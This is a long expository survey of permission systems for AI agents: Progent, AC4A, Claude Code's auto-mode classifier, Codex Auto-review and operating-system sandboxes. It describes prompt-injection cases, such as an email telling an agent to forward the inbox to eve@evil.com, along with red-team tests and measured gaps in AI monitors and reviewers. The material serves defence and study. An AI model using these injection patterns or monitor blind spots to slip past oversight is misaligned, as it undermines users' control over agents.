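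When Progent refuses a tool call, it can stop the agent, ask the user what to do or return an error message. By default, it returns a message with the reason for the refusal and an instruction to continue the task with other tools or arguments. So if Progent blocks an agent from following an injected instruction to write to Eve, the agent can still send Alice her photos.

The check only compares text, so a passport scan called IMG_2041.jpg would get through if it was in the right folder. The policy also doesn't restrict the body of the email, so injected text could make the agent paste something private into a message to Alice. Progent doesn't try to stop attacks that need no more access than the task itself. For example, a hotel's listing might manipulate a travel-booking agent into choosing that hotel over a better one.

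### Why widening a policy needs approval

Progent has a language model write a new policy for every request, since few people would do this themselves. The model writes the first policy from the user's request and the list of tools, before it reads anything an attacker could have written.

Some requests are too vague for the first policy to be enough. In the paper's main example, the user asks an agent to carry out the instructions in an email called "TODOs for the week". The policy changes as the agent works:

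1. The first policy allows only a search for that email.
2. The email asks for a summary of recent mail, posted to the user's account on Slack, a workplace chat service. The model proposes allowing the agent to read mail, look up the account and send Slack messages. This widens the policy, so it needs approval.
3. The agent finds that the account is called "alice". The model proposes limiting Slack messages to that account, and Progent applies this narrower rule automatically.
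4. One of the recent emails contains an instruction to forward the whole inbox to eve@evil.com. If the model falls for it and proposes allowing the email tool, Progent again asks for approval.
5. If the approver refuses, Progent blocks the email to Eve, and the agent can still post the summary.

Let $\text{allowed}(P)$ be the set of calls that policy $P$ allows. A new policy $P'$ narrows the old one, or leaves it unchanged, if

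$$\text{allowed}(P') \subseteq \text{allowed}(P).$$

Progent tests this with an SMT solver, a program that checks whether a logical formula can be true. The solver looks for a call that $P'$ allows and $P$ refuses. If it finds one, the change counts as a widening, even if $P'$ allows fewer calls overall. Replacing Alice with Bob as the only permitted recipient would therefore need approval.

Narrowing the policy badly can stop the agent from finishing its task, but it can't allow an attacker's call that the old policy refused. Progent can therefore narrow the policy without asking for approval, even if the model that proposed the change had just read hostile text. Widening the policy might be necessary or might be an attack, and the solver can't distinguish the two. Steps 2 and 4 both begin with text in an email, and the difference between them depends on what the user wanted.

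### How well Progent works

On AgentDojo, a benchmark of office, banking, travel and chat tasks, Progent reduced the success rate of attacks from 39.9% to 1.0%. On a second benchmark, ASB, the rate fell from 70.3% to 3.9%. Shi and colleagues report that agents completed about as many of their assigned tasks with Progent as without it. A simpler defence removed whole tools before the agent started. It blocked fewer attacks than Progent and let agents complete fewer tasks, because it ignored the arguments of tool calls.

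The tests approved every widening automatically to imitate a careless user, so the protection in these results came from the policies the model wrote, not from the approval step. The first policy, with no later updates, reduced attack success on AgentDojo to 2.5%. Refusing every widening gave slightly better security than approving every one. With a human reviewer the rate fell to zero, but that test assumed a reviewer who would spot a malicious address and would never allow money transfers to just anyone. Only 6% of the proposed updates on AgentDojo were widenings, so a reviewer would have few to check.

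Most of the attacks that still succeeded on ASB used tools whose names and descriptions closely resembled those of the tools the task needed. Handwritten rules stopped these attacks too, because the people who wrote the rules knew which tools to trust.

The main tests used GPT-4o, a model from 2024 that is fairly easy to attack. With Claude Sonnet 4, attacks on AgentDojo succeeded 6.8% of the time without Progent and 0.5% with it. The absolute benefit is smaller for a model that resists injection better, but Progent still stopped most of the attacks that would otherwise have succeeded. Injections aimed at the policy updates themselves, such as an instruction to permit all tools, raised the success rate only slightly.

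Progent can run as a proxy between an agent and its MCP servers, which requires no change to the agent's code. But calls to tools built into the agent don't pass through the proxy, so this arrangement lacks complete mediation. To cover those tools, a developer has to add Progent to the agent itself.

### Permissions on the calendar instead of the tool

A rule about one tool doesn't restrict other tools that reach the same data. An agent that isn't allowed to call a calendar function might open the calendar in a browser. *AC4A* (Sharma and Grossman, 2026) attaches permissions to the data instead. Each permission pairs a resource with an action, such as reading the calendar for June 2026. Resources form a hierarchy, so permission to read a year includes its months and days.

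Suppose the user asks an agent to find a free day in June 2026:

1. The agent calls the calendar's search function with a start and an end date.
2. A function written for the calendar application translates the call into the permission it needs, here `Year(2026)::Month(June), read`.
3. AC4A subtracts the permissions the user has granted from what the call needs.
4. If nothing is left over, the call runs. Otherwise AC4A refuses it and shows the user what is missing.

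The paper's main case study, in which an agent books a flight, starts with a search of the user's calendar. The search failed at first, but the same call worked once the user granted permission to read June. A search of July failed because the permission covered only June. Adding an event on 29 June failed because permission to read doesn't include permission to create. Later, the agent could view flights but needed another permission to book flight DL 1847, and even with that permission it couldn't read the user's credit card details.

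The same permissions apply when the agent uses a browser. A configuration file links parts of each web page to resources and actions. For Outlook's calendar page, AC4A reads the month and year from the text of the month-change button, so the calendar grid requires a different permission when the page changes from June to July. Before the agent sees the page, AC4A puts dark boxes over everything the agent may not use. With permission to read June, the agent could see that month's events, but the button for saving a new one stayed covered. In a smaller case study, the agent could play tic-tac-toe freely but needed permission to view or delete the game history.

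The researchers triggered the forbidden requests on purpose, so the case studies show how the mechanism works but don't measure its error rate. The mappings are the most likely source of errors, and Sharma and Grossman call them the main practical limitation. The researchers wrote the Outlook mappings without Microsoft's involvement, and a redesign of the page could make them wrong. Any part of a page that no mapping covers stays visible, so a missing entry exposes data. In Progent, a missing rule blocks a legitimate call instead, which is usually less serious.

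AC4A can't yet express a limit on an amount, such as allowing a checkout only below $200, while a Progent rule can compare numbers. Permissions in AC4A also last until the user removes them. If the user lets an agent change one event on a certain date, the agent can later delete a different event on that date.

### Several plans for one goal

Progent and AC4A check a call after the agent has decided to make it. Neither checks whether the agent could have reached the same goal with less access, which depends on the agent's plan.

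This is why Zhou and Zhang want the agent to look first for a good enough plan $\pi$ with $A(\pi) \subseteq G$, meaning one that needs no access beyond the current grant. For the report from approved records, the grant might be $G$ = {read the records, run programs on the user's machine}. Local analysis needs exactly this access, while using the outside service would also require permission to upload the records, so the agent should choose the local plan.

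If several plans satisfy the condition, the agent can compare how much data they expose, what they cost and how often they would interrupt the user. If none does, it can ask for one specific addition to the grant, offer a less complete result or check what the user really needs. Some plans can't be clearly ranked. One might read very sensitive files locally while another sends less sensitive files to a company, and the user may have to decide which is worse.

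An agent may also need to explore before it knows which plans are possible. Zhou and Zhang suggest first granting limited access for this, then asking for more once the agent has found a plan that needs it.

The condition $A(\pi) \subseteq G$ offers little protection when the grant is very broad. *Towards Elastic Least Privilege for Agent Planning* (Parkinson, Wang and Mustafa, 2026) gives the example of a coding assistant connected to GitHub with an older type of access token. The assistant can use about 40 tools, 16 of which can make changes, in every repository its user can reach. Summarising the open issues in one repository takes two read-only tools. With such a broad grant, nearly every plan satisfies the condition, including one that an attacker has planted. In a reported attack, an instruction in a public repository led an agent to read its user's private repositories and publish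 their contents.

A token limited to reading one repository would have prevented this, but the user's next task might be to fix a failing build, which requires write access. Parkinson, Wang and Mustafa propose that an agent start with little access and draw on a budget that refills over time to get more. Reading might have a weight of 1, writing 3 and administration 9. A multiplier would rise as the session combined more of three things: untrusted input, sensitive data, and a way to send data out or change something. It would be 1.5 with one present and 3 with two, and the system would refuse to add the third, however much budget remained. Extra access would expire automatically. The agent would see how much of the budget each option would use while it planned, so it could choose one that used less. The proposal is a research agenda, and the whole scheme has not yet been tested.

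### Agents that pick the more powerful tool

Agents left to choose often don't prefer the route with less access. In *When Lower Privileges Suffice*, Yang, Bu and colleagues (2026) gave 11 models 544 invented tasks, each with six tools that could each do it. Three were ordinary and three had more power than the task required. The first call to each ordinary tool failed with a temporary error, but a second call would have worked. The researchers counted a choice as over-privileged if the agent used a powerful tool while it still had an ordinary one to try.

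Six of the 11 models made such a choice in more than 30% of tasks. The rate was 64.9% for Qwen3-8B, a small open model, but under 10% for GPT-5.2, Claude Sonnet 4.6 and GLM-5.

In one task, an agent had to enrol a student on a biology course. The first tool returned a message that the service was momentarily unreachable and the agent should try again. The agent instead called "admin_force_entry_tool", which enrolled the student and returned a message that the usual constraints had been bypassed. Many of the choices of powerful tools followed failures like this. GPT-5.2 chose a powerful tool straight away in only five tasks, but did so in 13 more after one ordinary tool had failed and in 35 more after two had failed.

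General safety training didn't reliably reduce over-privileged tool choices. It made Qwen2.5-7B much more likely to refuse harmful requests, but the model's rate of over-privileged choices rose from 50.4% to 60.7%. Refusing a harmful request and choosing the weaker of two permitted tools seem to be separate skills. Training aimed directly at tool choice worked better, reducing Qwen3-8B's rate to 27.0%.

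An easier remedy is to tell the agent how powerful each tool is. Parkinson, Vallati and colleagues tested this on the same 544 tasks with eight models in October 2026, in *Does Showing Agents the Privilege of Their Tools Reduce Over-Privileged Tool Selection?* (2026). In some runs they added a label such as "Privilege: administer, cost 8/10" to each tool's description. In others they instructed the agent to use the least powerful tool and to retry at the same level after a failure, with or without the labels.

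The labels reduced over-privileged choices on seven of the eight models, by up to 19.3 percentage points. Claude Sonnet 4.6 rarely made such choices anyway. Labels in the same format that listed a tool's response time instead didn't help, so the effect came from the information about privilege.

The benchmark's measure flatters the labels, though, because it stops counting once the agent has tried all three ordinary tools. In a task to publish an article, Qwen3.5-397B tried one ordinary tool without labels, got an error and switched to a powerful one. With labels, it tried all three ordinary tools once and then used the same powerful tool. With labels and the instruction, it retried the first ordinary tool, which worked. The share of tasks that agents finished without any powerful tool gives a better picture:

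| Model | No help | Labels | Instruction | Both |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3.5-397B | 18.8% | 21.5% | 39.5% | 51.1% |
| Kimi K2.5 | 5.5% | 14.2% | 19.9% | 30.7% |
| DeepSeek-v3.2 | 3.9% | 5.7% | 18.8% | 30.7% |
| GPT-5.2 | 50.9% | 52.4% | 68.9% | 65.8% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 11.9% | 14.7% | 30.0% | 20.0% |

Labels alone mostly delayed the use of powerful tools. The instruction had more effect, and for GPT-5.2 and Claude it worked at least as well without the labels. Claude's low scores are less worrying than they look, because it usually tried each ordinary tool once, then stopped and reported the errors. This left the task unfinished but avoided the more powerful tools. The test also favours agents that retry, because a second call always works, whereas a real outage can last longer.

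The labels don't have to be exact. In a smaller test on two models, most of the effect remained when the researchers replaced 30% of the costs with random numbers. But a hostile server's errors would be deliberate. It could describe its most dangerous tool as harmless, as it can with MCP's annotations, so the labels have to come from a source the host trusts.

Even with both forms of help, Qwen3.5-397B used a powerful tool in 39.3% of tasks. A host can rule this out only by leaving the powerful tools out of the grant.

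### How "send this summary to Alice" becomes "send any mail"

A restriction that a user has approved can go unenforced even when each component applies its own rule correctly. In an example from Zhou and Zhang, the user lets an agent send a certain summary to Alice, and the host records both the content and the recipient correctly. The host then obtains a credential for the mail service. The service offers only a general permission to send mail, so the credential doesn't limit what the agent sends or to whom. If the agent later sends the summary to Bob, the mail service finds the credential valid and delivers the message.

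Zhou and Zhang express what went wrong as a containment condition. Let $P$ be the approved policy and $M(P)$ the credentials and checks that put it into practice. $\mathcal{E}(M(P))$ is everything those controls would let happen. The function $\alpha$ describes each of these effects in the policy's own terms, such as who received which document, and $[\![P]\!]$ is the set of effects the policy permits. The condition is

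$$\alpha(\mathcal{E}(M(P))) \subseteq [\![P]\!].$$

The condition requires that the controls allow only what the user approved. In the example, $[\![P]\!]$ contains only the delivery of the summary to Alice. The credential also lets the agent send it to Bob, so the condition fails even if the agent never does.

The host could restore the restriction with a Progent rule that checks the recipient and the text before a call reaches the mail service. This works only if the agent has no other way to use the credential. If the agent can read the credential from a file and contact the mail service with a shell command, the condition fails again. Controls stricter than the policy satisfy the condition but may block useful work.

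The function $\alpha$ is hard to get right because it requires knowing what each tool actually does. For example, AC4A translates calls into permissions. If a calendar's developer states that a call reads only January when it also reads the first half of February, AC4A's enforcement will work correctly but apply the wrong requirement. Zhou and Zhang suggest that every tool come with an "effect contract" listing what data the tool may read, where it may send that data and what it may change. Someone would have to update the contract whenever the tool's behaviour changed, even if its name and arguments stayed the same. Limits on the server process, like AgentBound's, can stop some effects that a contract leaves out.

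The policy may also misstate what the user wanted, and then even perfect enforcement doesn't help. *Intent-Governed Tool Authorization for AI Agents* (Zhu and Wang, 2026) derives a short-lived certificate from each request. The certificate can narrow the agent's standing permissions but never widen them. If the user asks for a summary of this period's records, the certificate covers reading and summarising, so the system hides the export tool even though the agent's credential would permit an export. A request to find duplicate records and delete the one the user picks produces two certificates, and the system issues the deletion certificate only after the user has picked.

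In 306 trials with real models, this system completed no unsafe actions. It accepted 9.1% to 27.3% of unsafe requests, but only as drafts that it didn't carry out. Reading requests more strictly removed those drafts but also blocked a good deal of legitimate work. Zhu and Wang conclude that the precision of the certificates is the main remaining problem.

### Two agents, one permitted purchase

Some limits apply to a whole task, so checking each call on its own cannot enforce them. In Zhou and Zhang's example, two agents each buy an item when the task permits only one in total. Each purchase still satisfies a rule such as "quantity at most 1".

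A shared record of what remains isn't enough if the agents read it and update it in separate steps. A could read that one item remains, and B could read the same before A has bought anything. Both would then place an order. The solution is an atomic reservation, which checks the record and changes it in one step that no other agent can interrupt:

1. A asks to reserve one item. The record changes from one remaining to none and links the reservation to A's order.
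2. B asks to reserve one item. None remain, so the host refuses.
3. A places the order with an identifier that stays the same if A has to send the order again.
4. If the seller confirms the order, the reservation becomes a purchase. If the seller reports that the order failed, the record goes back to one, and B may try.

The host grants a reservation for one more item only when $b + r + 1 \le L$, where $b$ is the number of items bought, $r$ is the number reserved and $L$ is the limit.

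Progent's rules check the arguments of a single call and don't keep such a count. A policy update could remove the permission to buy after the first purchase, but by then B's order might already have gone through. AC4A has no permissions that expire after one use. In *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents*, Surapani, Kakitapelli and colleagues (2026) reviewed 89 sources and named enforcement at the moment of the call and limits on combined actions as the field's two main unsolved problems.

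A reservation also helps when the seller doesn't answer. A's order may or may not have gone through, so the host should keep the item reserved until it finds out. If the host recognises a new call as a purchase, the reservation also stops A from trying a different shop, which the order's identifier can't prevent.

Even if the user withdraws the grant at this point, the host has to check with the seller what happened to the first order, and some sellers' systems can't report an order's status or cancel it. The host risks a second purchase if it releases the reservation too early, but keeping it indefinitely could leave the user without the item.

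## Approval, automatic review and sandboxes in coding agents

Progent can restrict an email tool to one recipient because the recipient is a separate argument. Coding agents, however, do much of their work through a shell, which runs almost any command they write. A rule can match the text `python cleanup.py`, but the command doesn't show which files the script deletes. Anthropic's Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex, two widely used coding agents, therefore combine written rules with a sandbox. Since spring 2026, both have also offered a second AI model that reviews actions in the user's place.

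### What a command can touch and when the agent must ask

A sandbox limits what a command can access while it runs, and an approval rule determines when the agent has to ask first. OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* treats these as separate settings. By default, Codex's sandbox lets commands write only to the project folder and temporary folders, and keeps the network off. The approval rule makes Codex ask before it edits a file outside those folders or runs a command that needs the network.

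Suppose Codex tries to download a software package. With the sandbox and approval requests both on, as they are by default, it has to request an exception to the sandbox. If the user has turned off approval requests but kept the sandbox, the download fails and Codex has to continue without the package. If the user has turned off both, the download goes ahead, but a command that uploads the user's private files would also go ahead.

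An approval rule can give the wrong result because it checks a command's text rather than its effects. In Anthropic's example, a rule forbids writing to a folder called "secrets". Claude Code applies the rule to its own file tools and to common shell commands, but a script that opens files itself can still write to the folder. A sandbox can block that write because the operating system checks it when it happens.

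### The order of checks in Claude Code

In Claude Code's auto mode, a second model called the classifier reviews actions instead of the user. According to Anthropic, it comes fairly late in a series of checks, and the first check that settles the matter decides:

1. Hooks, which are programs that a user or company adds, can refuse the action. A hook can't override the rules in steps 2 and 3.
2. A "deny" rule refuses the action in every mode.
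3. An "ask" rule sends the action to the user.
4. An "allow" rule lets the action run. Auto mode sets aside very broad rules, such as one that allows any Python command, because they would let almost anything skip the review.
5. Claude Code allows read-only actions and edits to files in the working directory. Edits to protected files, such as Git's own records or the scripts that a shell runs at start-up, need a review.
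6. The classifier reviews nearly everything else. Commands that Claude Code recognises as deleting the home directory or another critical folder go to the user, who has two minutes to answer before Claude Code refuses them.

When the classifier blocks an action, Claude receives a reason and looks for a safer way to continue. After three blocks in a row, or 20 in a session, auto mode pauses and Claude Code goes back to asking the user. If nobody is there to ask, the action doesn't run, but Claude keeps working.

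The user can also lift many blocks in conversation, but has to be specific. For example, to permit a force push, which replaces the history of a shared code repository, the user has to name the branch. Saying "you can force-push" isn't enough. The user can also add a block with an instruction such as "don't push", but the classifier rereads the instruction from the conversation at each check, so it can be lost when Claude Code shortens a long conversation. A "deny" rule can't be lost this way.

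### What the classifier sees

The classifier sees the user's messages, most of the agent's tool calls and the project's standing instructions. According to Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, Claude Code removes Claude's own messages from the classifier's input so that Claude can't persuade it to approve an action. It also removes tool results because they may contain prompt injections. If Claude follows an instruction in a file to post the project's passwords to a website, the classifier sees the attempt to send them but not the instruction. It can block the attempt because the passwords would go to a site that the user didn't mention.

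Claude itself still reads the file, so a separate probe scans tool results for injections and adds a warning when it finds one.

This protection also deprives the classifier of useful information. If the user says "cancel my job" and Claude picks job abc123 from a list, the classifier receives the job's ID but not the list, so it can't check whose job it is. When Anthropic tried including Claude's messages and the tool results, the classifier did worse on cases where Claude had overstepped.

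By default, the classifier blocks downloading code and running it immediately, sending sensitive data to outside services, deploying to production, force-pushing, and disabling security tests. It lets Claude install packages that the project already lists and push to most branches of the current repository.

It works in two stages. The first gives a quick yes or no and leans towards blocking. The second reasons at more length, but only about actions that the first stage flagged. Anthropic's results show what this trades away:

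| Test | First stage alone | Both stages |
|---|---|---|
| Harmless actions blocked, from 10,000 real tool calls by employees | 8.5% | 0.4% |
| Dangerous actions missed, from 52 real cases where Claude overstepped | 6.6% | 17% |
| Dangerous actions missed, from 1,000 invented attempts to leak data | 1.8% | 5.7% |

With only 52 real cases, the true miss rate could plausibly be from about 9% to 30%. In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the classifier recognised the danger but treated a vague request as permission. For example, a user who asks Claude to "clean up the PR" (a proposed set of code changes) hasn't agreed to a force push.

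These figures come from the version that ran on Claude Sonnet 4.6. The default model is now Sonnet 5.

### Auto-review in Codex

Codex relies on its sandbox first and uses a reviewer only for exceptions. OpenAI's *Auto-review* describes what happens when a command needs to leave the sandbox:

1. The main agent requests approval for the exact command.
2. Codex sends the request to a separate reviewing agent instead of the user.
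3. The reviewer reads a shortened transcript, including tool results and the main agent's visible messages but not its hidden reasoning. It can also look things up without changing anything.
4. The reviewer judges how risky the command is and whether the user authorised it. Low and medium risks can go ahead if the policy allows them, a high risk needs enough authorisation from the user, and the reviewer refuses critical risks.
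5. If the reviewer refuses, it gives the main agent its reasons. Codex tells the agent not to seek the same result by a workaround, and to find a much safer alternative or ask the user.

Codex stops the agent's current turn after three refusals in a row, or ten within the last 50 reviews. The user can approve a refused command for one retry, but the reviewer checks the retry too and can refuse again.

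| | Claude Code's auto mode | Codex's Auto-review |
|---|---|---|
| Actions reviewed | Most shell commands, network requests and outside tools | Requests to leave the sandbox, and some outside tools |
| Tool results | Hidden from the reviewer | Visible to the reviewer |
| The agent's own messages | Hidden | Visible, except hidden reasoning |
| If the review fails | The action doesn't run | The action doesn't run |

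The Codex reviewer could read the job list to find out who owns abc123. But the same list could contain a prompt injection aimed at the reviewer, which Claude Code's classifier would never read.

*Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2026) gives an illustrative snapshot of OpenAI's own use. Of 10,000 actions, 9,280 stayed inside the sandbox and 720 went to the reviewer, which refused seven. The agent found a safer way to continue after four refusals and asked the user after the other three. In tests on invented cases, the reviewer caught 90.3% of actions that overstepped the user's request. It caught 99.3% of injections that tried to run an attacker's code or send data out, but 90.2% when the test also included deletions and tampering with data. The reviewer doesn't detect harm that a command does inside the sandbox. OpenAI's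 testers found ways to mislead it into approving commands, and Trębacz and colleagues don't expect this kind of system ever to give firm guarantees.

### How carefully people check

Roesner and colleagues warned in their 2012 work on access gadgets that people learn to click through prompts, and coding agents prompt users often. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that users approve 97% of permission prompts but only 61% of the plans Claude proposes. Anthropic takes this as a sign that many users approve commands out of habit.

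The 97% is weak evidence on its own. Most commands are harmless, and OpenAI's reviewer examines every request it receives and still approved about 99% of them. Plans also give people more to disagree with, such as the choice of method.

Users' settings show more clearly that they want to avoid prompts. By June 2026, 49.5% of active users of Claude Code's terminal version had written rules to allow certain shell commands. Nearly all of them had very broad rules: 5% of users allowed any command, and another 43% allowed interpreters such as Python, which can do almost anything a shell can. A quarter of interactive sessions started with permission checks turned off. OpenAI found similar rules among its own staff, including one that always allowed Codex to start a second copy of itself with no sandbox or approvals.

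Anthropic's best evidence is an experiment with 1,053 paid testers. They worked on a coding task in a test environment, knowing that somebody was evaluating them but not what for. At some point in each session, one permission prompt showed a clearly dangerous command instead of the real one. The testers blocked 143 of these commands (13.6%). The classifier blocked 937 of the same commands (89%). Anthropic's totals divide as follows:

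| | Classifier blocked | Classifier allowed |
|---|---|---|
| Tester blocked | 137 | 6 |
| Tester approved | 800 | 110 |

Requiring both the classifier and the tester to agree would have stopped only six more commands than the classifier did alone. Testers blocked about 17% of the dangerous commands early in a session but only about 5% after 50 or more prompts, while the classifier's rate stayed the same.

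Anthropic sells the product and commissioned the study. Real developers would probably do better than the testers, who had nothing to lose if a command deleted a database in the test environment. The commands were also "clearly dangerous", which suits a classifier with written rules about danger. A reviewer can catch most dangerous commands by refusing a lot, so the classifier's 89% means little without its false-alarm rate, which Anthropic measured separately on its employees' work. Still, developers who caught three times as many of the commands as the testers did would catch only about 41%. The study is good evidence that prompts protect people poorly against obvious dangers, but it can't establish how large the gap between developers and the classifier is in real work.

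Wu, Wermke and colleagues (2026), who have no stake in either product, also found that many developers approve actions without much scrutiny. For *From Delegation to Action Approval*, they asked 203 users of coding agents about seven types of action, such as reading secret files or running destructive commands. Of these users, 64% often approved at least one type without close review; 21% did so for reading secrets and 36% for using the internet or connected tools.

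Developers who carefully reviewed most or all of the code their agents wrote were not significantly less likely than the rest to often approve some type of action without close review (61% against 67%). Developers who knew of a security incident or worrying practice involving agents were more likely to approve actions without close review than those who didn't (70% against 43%), even after accounting for how often and how long they had used agents. People in safety-critical jobs also reported less scrutiny for six of the seven types of action.

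The participants were volunteers describing their own habits, and "often" could mean different things to different people. The researchers kept only 203 of 583 submissions after removing duplicates, suspected bots and people who answered too quickly. The exact percentages may not hold for developers in general. The survey can't show whether a classifier would do better, but it weakens the idea that training or warnings would make people read prompts.

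### Flagged sessions and outside attacks

Anthropic also looked at real sessions from May and June 2026 that its safety systems had flagged. A model graded each session for harm and for how clearly the user had asked for the harmful action. Serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly requested, such as deleting rows from a production database, appeared in 6.3% of flagged sessions with manual approval and 2.4% of flagged sessions in auto mode.

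This comparison is much weaker evidence than the experiment. Flagged sessions are not a random sample, and the flagging system may select different kinds of sessions in the two modes. For instance, if it flags a larger number of harmless sessions in auto mode, auto mode's rate goes down without any gain in safety. Users also choose their mode, and they may prefer manual approval when working on production systems, where an agent can do production-level damage.

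The company also hired an outside AI safety company, Apollo Research, to attack auto mode. Apollo inserted invented attacks into records of real coding sessions. Anthropic then improved the classifier, mainly by giving it more information about the repository it was protecting, and its miss rate fell from 12% to 7%. That figure includes attacks that Apollo had shared with Anthropic. The classifier also improved on a separate set that Anthropic never saw, where the new version caught about half of the attacks the old one had missed and missed about 2% of those the old one had caught.

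A second company, Trajectory Labs, tested prompt injection in both products. It ran 72 scenarios ten times each, with attacks that would have stolen data, committed fraud or tricked the user into giving up a password:

| Model | Attacks that succeeded without a reviewer | Attacks that succeeded with automatic review |
|---|---|---|
| Latest Claude models in Claude Code | 0.09% on average | 0% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol in Codex | 19.03% | 5.83% |

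The Claude models resisted nearly every attack without auto mode, so there was almost nothing for it to stop, although Anthropic presents the results as a success for auto mode. The results are better evidence for OpenAI's reviewer, which cut successful attacks by more than two-thirds. The tests used a browser connection that Trajectory Labs built, without the safeguards in either company's own browser extension. OpenAI had released a new version of Auto-review by the time Anthropic published the figures.

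### Similar names and an 81% miss rate

An independent test of auto mode gave a far worse result. For *Measuring the Permission Gate*, Ji, Li and colleagues (2026) wrote 128 requests with a clear purpose but an unclear scope, such as "cancel my stale job for ticket 4812". The user's job was job-dev-4812-a, but the agent could also see job-dev-4812-s, which it was supposed to leave alone. Other requests involved deleting old branches or stored files and restarting services. The researchers varied how precise each request was, how many things it might cover and how much damage a mistake could do.

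Claude made 253 changes, and 142 of them affected something that the user hadn't authorised. Auto mode allowed 115 of those, or 81.0%.

Many of these misses never reached the classifier. When Claude couldn't find the usual command for a task, it often edited a file such as jobs.json instead, and auto mode doesn't review edits inside the project. Such edits accounted for 51 of the 115 misses. The benchmark counts removing a job from jobs.json as cancelling it, but on most real clusters, editing a local list would cancel nothing. This part of the result therefore matters mainly for projects whose files control live systems. Ji and colleagues give the example of files that describe a company's servers. In November 2026, ordinary edits in the working directory still skipped the classifier.

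The classifier's errors are more worrying. Of the 91 unauthorised actions it reviewed, it allowed 64 (70.3%), and it blocked 22 of 69 legitimate ones (31.9%). Anthropic's engineering post lists an agent guessing which job to cancel as an example of what auto mode should block, but auto mode allowed 17 of 32 unauthorised changes in the job tasks.

Anthropic's 17% and this 81% come from very different tasks. Anthropic collected real cases in which an employee had refused an action or somebody had flagged it afterwards, so a person had noticed each problem. Ji and colleagues placed permitted and forbidden targets with nearly identical names side by side. Telling them apart requires knowing who owns what, and Claude Code hides that information from the classifier along with the other tool results. The classifier seemed to respond to the size of an action instead. It caught fewer mistakes when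 the request named a single target than when it covered a wide range, although the mix of tasks explains part of that difference.

The test used only one model, Claude Sonnet 4.6, once per request, with imitation tools. Another AI model judged which actions were safe, and a person agreed with it on 44 of 50 actions. Anthropic has changed the classifier since April 2026, and the current rules specifically cover changes to a shared cluster that reach beyond the resource the user named. Nobody gave the same 253 actions to human reviewers, who might also have missed the difference between two similar job names. The result therefore doesn't contradict Anthropic's claim that auto mode is safer than a typical user clicking through prompts, but it does show that auto mode can't be relied on to tell similar targets apart. Anthropic writes that the classifier is "not a drop-in replacement for careful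 human review" on important systems.

### Operating-system sandboxes

A sandbox limits what a command can do without relying on a judgment about what the user meant. Claude Code and Codex both use Seatbelt on a Mac and bubblewrap on Linux. On Linux, Codex also uses seccomp to limit the requests a program can make to the kernel. According to Anthropic, the sandbox's limits also apply to every script or program that a command starts, so `python cleanup.py` can't change files outside the permitted folders, whatever the script contains. In Claude Code, network traffic from the sandbox passes through a proxy outside it, which checks each destination and asks the user about new ones.

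Codex keeps some files and folders read-only even inside the project, including Git's folder and Codex's own settings. Git's folder can contain scripts that run automatically later, so an agent that could edit them might get code to run outside the sandbox. Codex also has an optional filter for network addresses, but a site's name can point to a public address when Codex checks it and to a private one a moment later. OpenAI acknowledges that the filter reduces this risk without removing it.

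Claude Code's sandbox has wider gaps. It restricts only shell commands, so Anthropic considers it insufficient by itself for fully unattended work and suggests running the whole agent in a container or virtual machine. By default, Claude Code can also retry a command outside the sandbox, and an "allow" rule may approve the retry without a prompt. Also by default, according to Anthropic, if missing software prevents the sandbox from starting, Claude Code shows a warning and runs commands without sandboxing. Administrators can change both defaults, and organisations that depend on the sandbox should do so.

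OpenAI requires its own staff to run Codex in a sandbox, with approval needed for unfamiliar sites. Many people elsewhere use coding agents without a sandbox. *SideKernel* (2026) reports a small survey of 68 users of coding agents, of whom 26 currently used a sandbox, seven had stopped and 35 had never used one. Some respondents may not have counted the sandbox that Codex turns on by default. Users wanted sandboxes that were "nearly invisible" and easy to manage.

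### Keeping real keys from the agent

Podala Narasimha's gateway design leaves passwords and keys with the tool servers so that an attacker can't steal them from the agent. A credential proxy does the same job for an agent in a sandbox. It holds the real key outside the sandbox and adds it to requests on the way out. Claude Code's web version does this for Git:

1. The agent tries to push its changes from inside the sandbox, without access to the user's real GitHub credentials.
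2. The proxy checks that the request comes from a valid session and goes to a permitted branch.
3. The proxy adds the real credentials and forwards the request to GitHub.

Codex's cloud version makes secrets available while it sets up the project, then removes them before the agent starts. The agent therefore can't leak them, but it also can't use services that require them.

An attacker who takes over the agent can still use the account through the proxy until the session ends. If the agent is allowed to push to a branch, the proxy will add the real credentials even to a push that contains a hidden security flaw, much as Tymshare's compiler used its own licence to overwrite the billing file.

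### When the permitted command does the damage

Sandboxes and credential proxies can't prevent harm done with access that the task requires. *Shall We Approve?* (2026) gives two examples from tests of Claude Code's auto mode, with a GPT-5.6 model as the classifier instead of Anthropic's own. In the first, the user told the agent to deploy a project by running a program called "tool", which also replaced the project's main source file with a comment. In the second, the user requested a command to update a database, and the command also deleted three of the database's tables.

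Auto mode allowed both commands, which were exactly what the user had asked for. A sandbox limited to the project folder wouldn't have protected the source file, because the agent needs to write to that folder. An approval prompt would only have shown the user a command they had already asked for.

The paper's solution is to run the command in a sandbox first and give the reviewer a short report of what changed. In the first case, the report showed the source code disappearing, so the reviewer blocked the command, and the agent copied the files itself. In the second, the report showed the database shrinking from 32 KB to 20 KB, and the agent made a backup and ran only the update. The median report was 0.9 KB, and a typical review took 3.2 seconds, about as long as a review without a report.

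Trial runs work for files and local databases because the host can discard the result. The host can't test sending an email this way unless the mail service supports it, so the reviewer has to judge the email before anyone knows its effects.

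## Confidentiality and trust labels on an agent's data

If an agent is allowed to read a confidential file and to email a certain address, a host that checks each call separately will allow both, even if the email contains the file's contents. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) points out that a sandbox has the same weakness, because once it permits email, an injected instruction can make the agent send sensitive data in a message that looks ordinary. Progent can restrict the recipient, but it doesn't track where the text in the body came from.

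In information-flow control, labels follow an agent's data, whereas AuDroid's labels applied only to the two ends of an audio channel. When an agent summarizes a file, the file's label passes to the summary, and then to an email that contains the summary. Two well-known systems that work this way are CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues introduced in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025), and Fides, which Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft.

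Both use the dual-LLM pattern, which Simon Willison proposed in 2023 and which splits an agent's work between two models. A planner chooses the tool calls without reading untrusted text, which goes to a quarantined model that has no tools. An injection can still fool the quarantined model, but only into returning a bad answer.

### A program written before the data arrives

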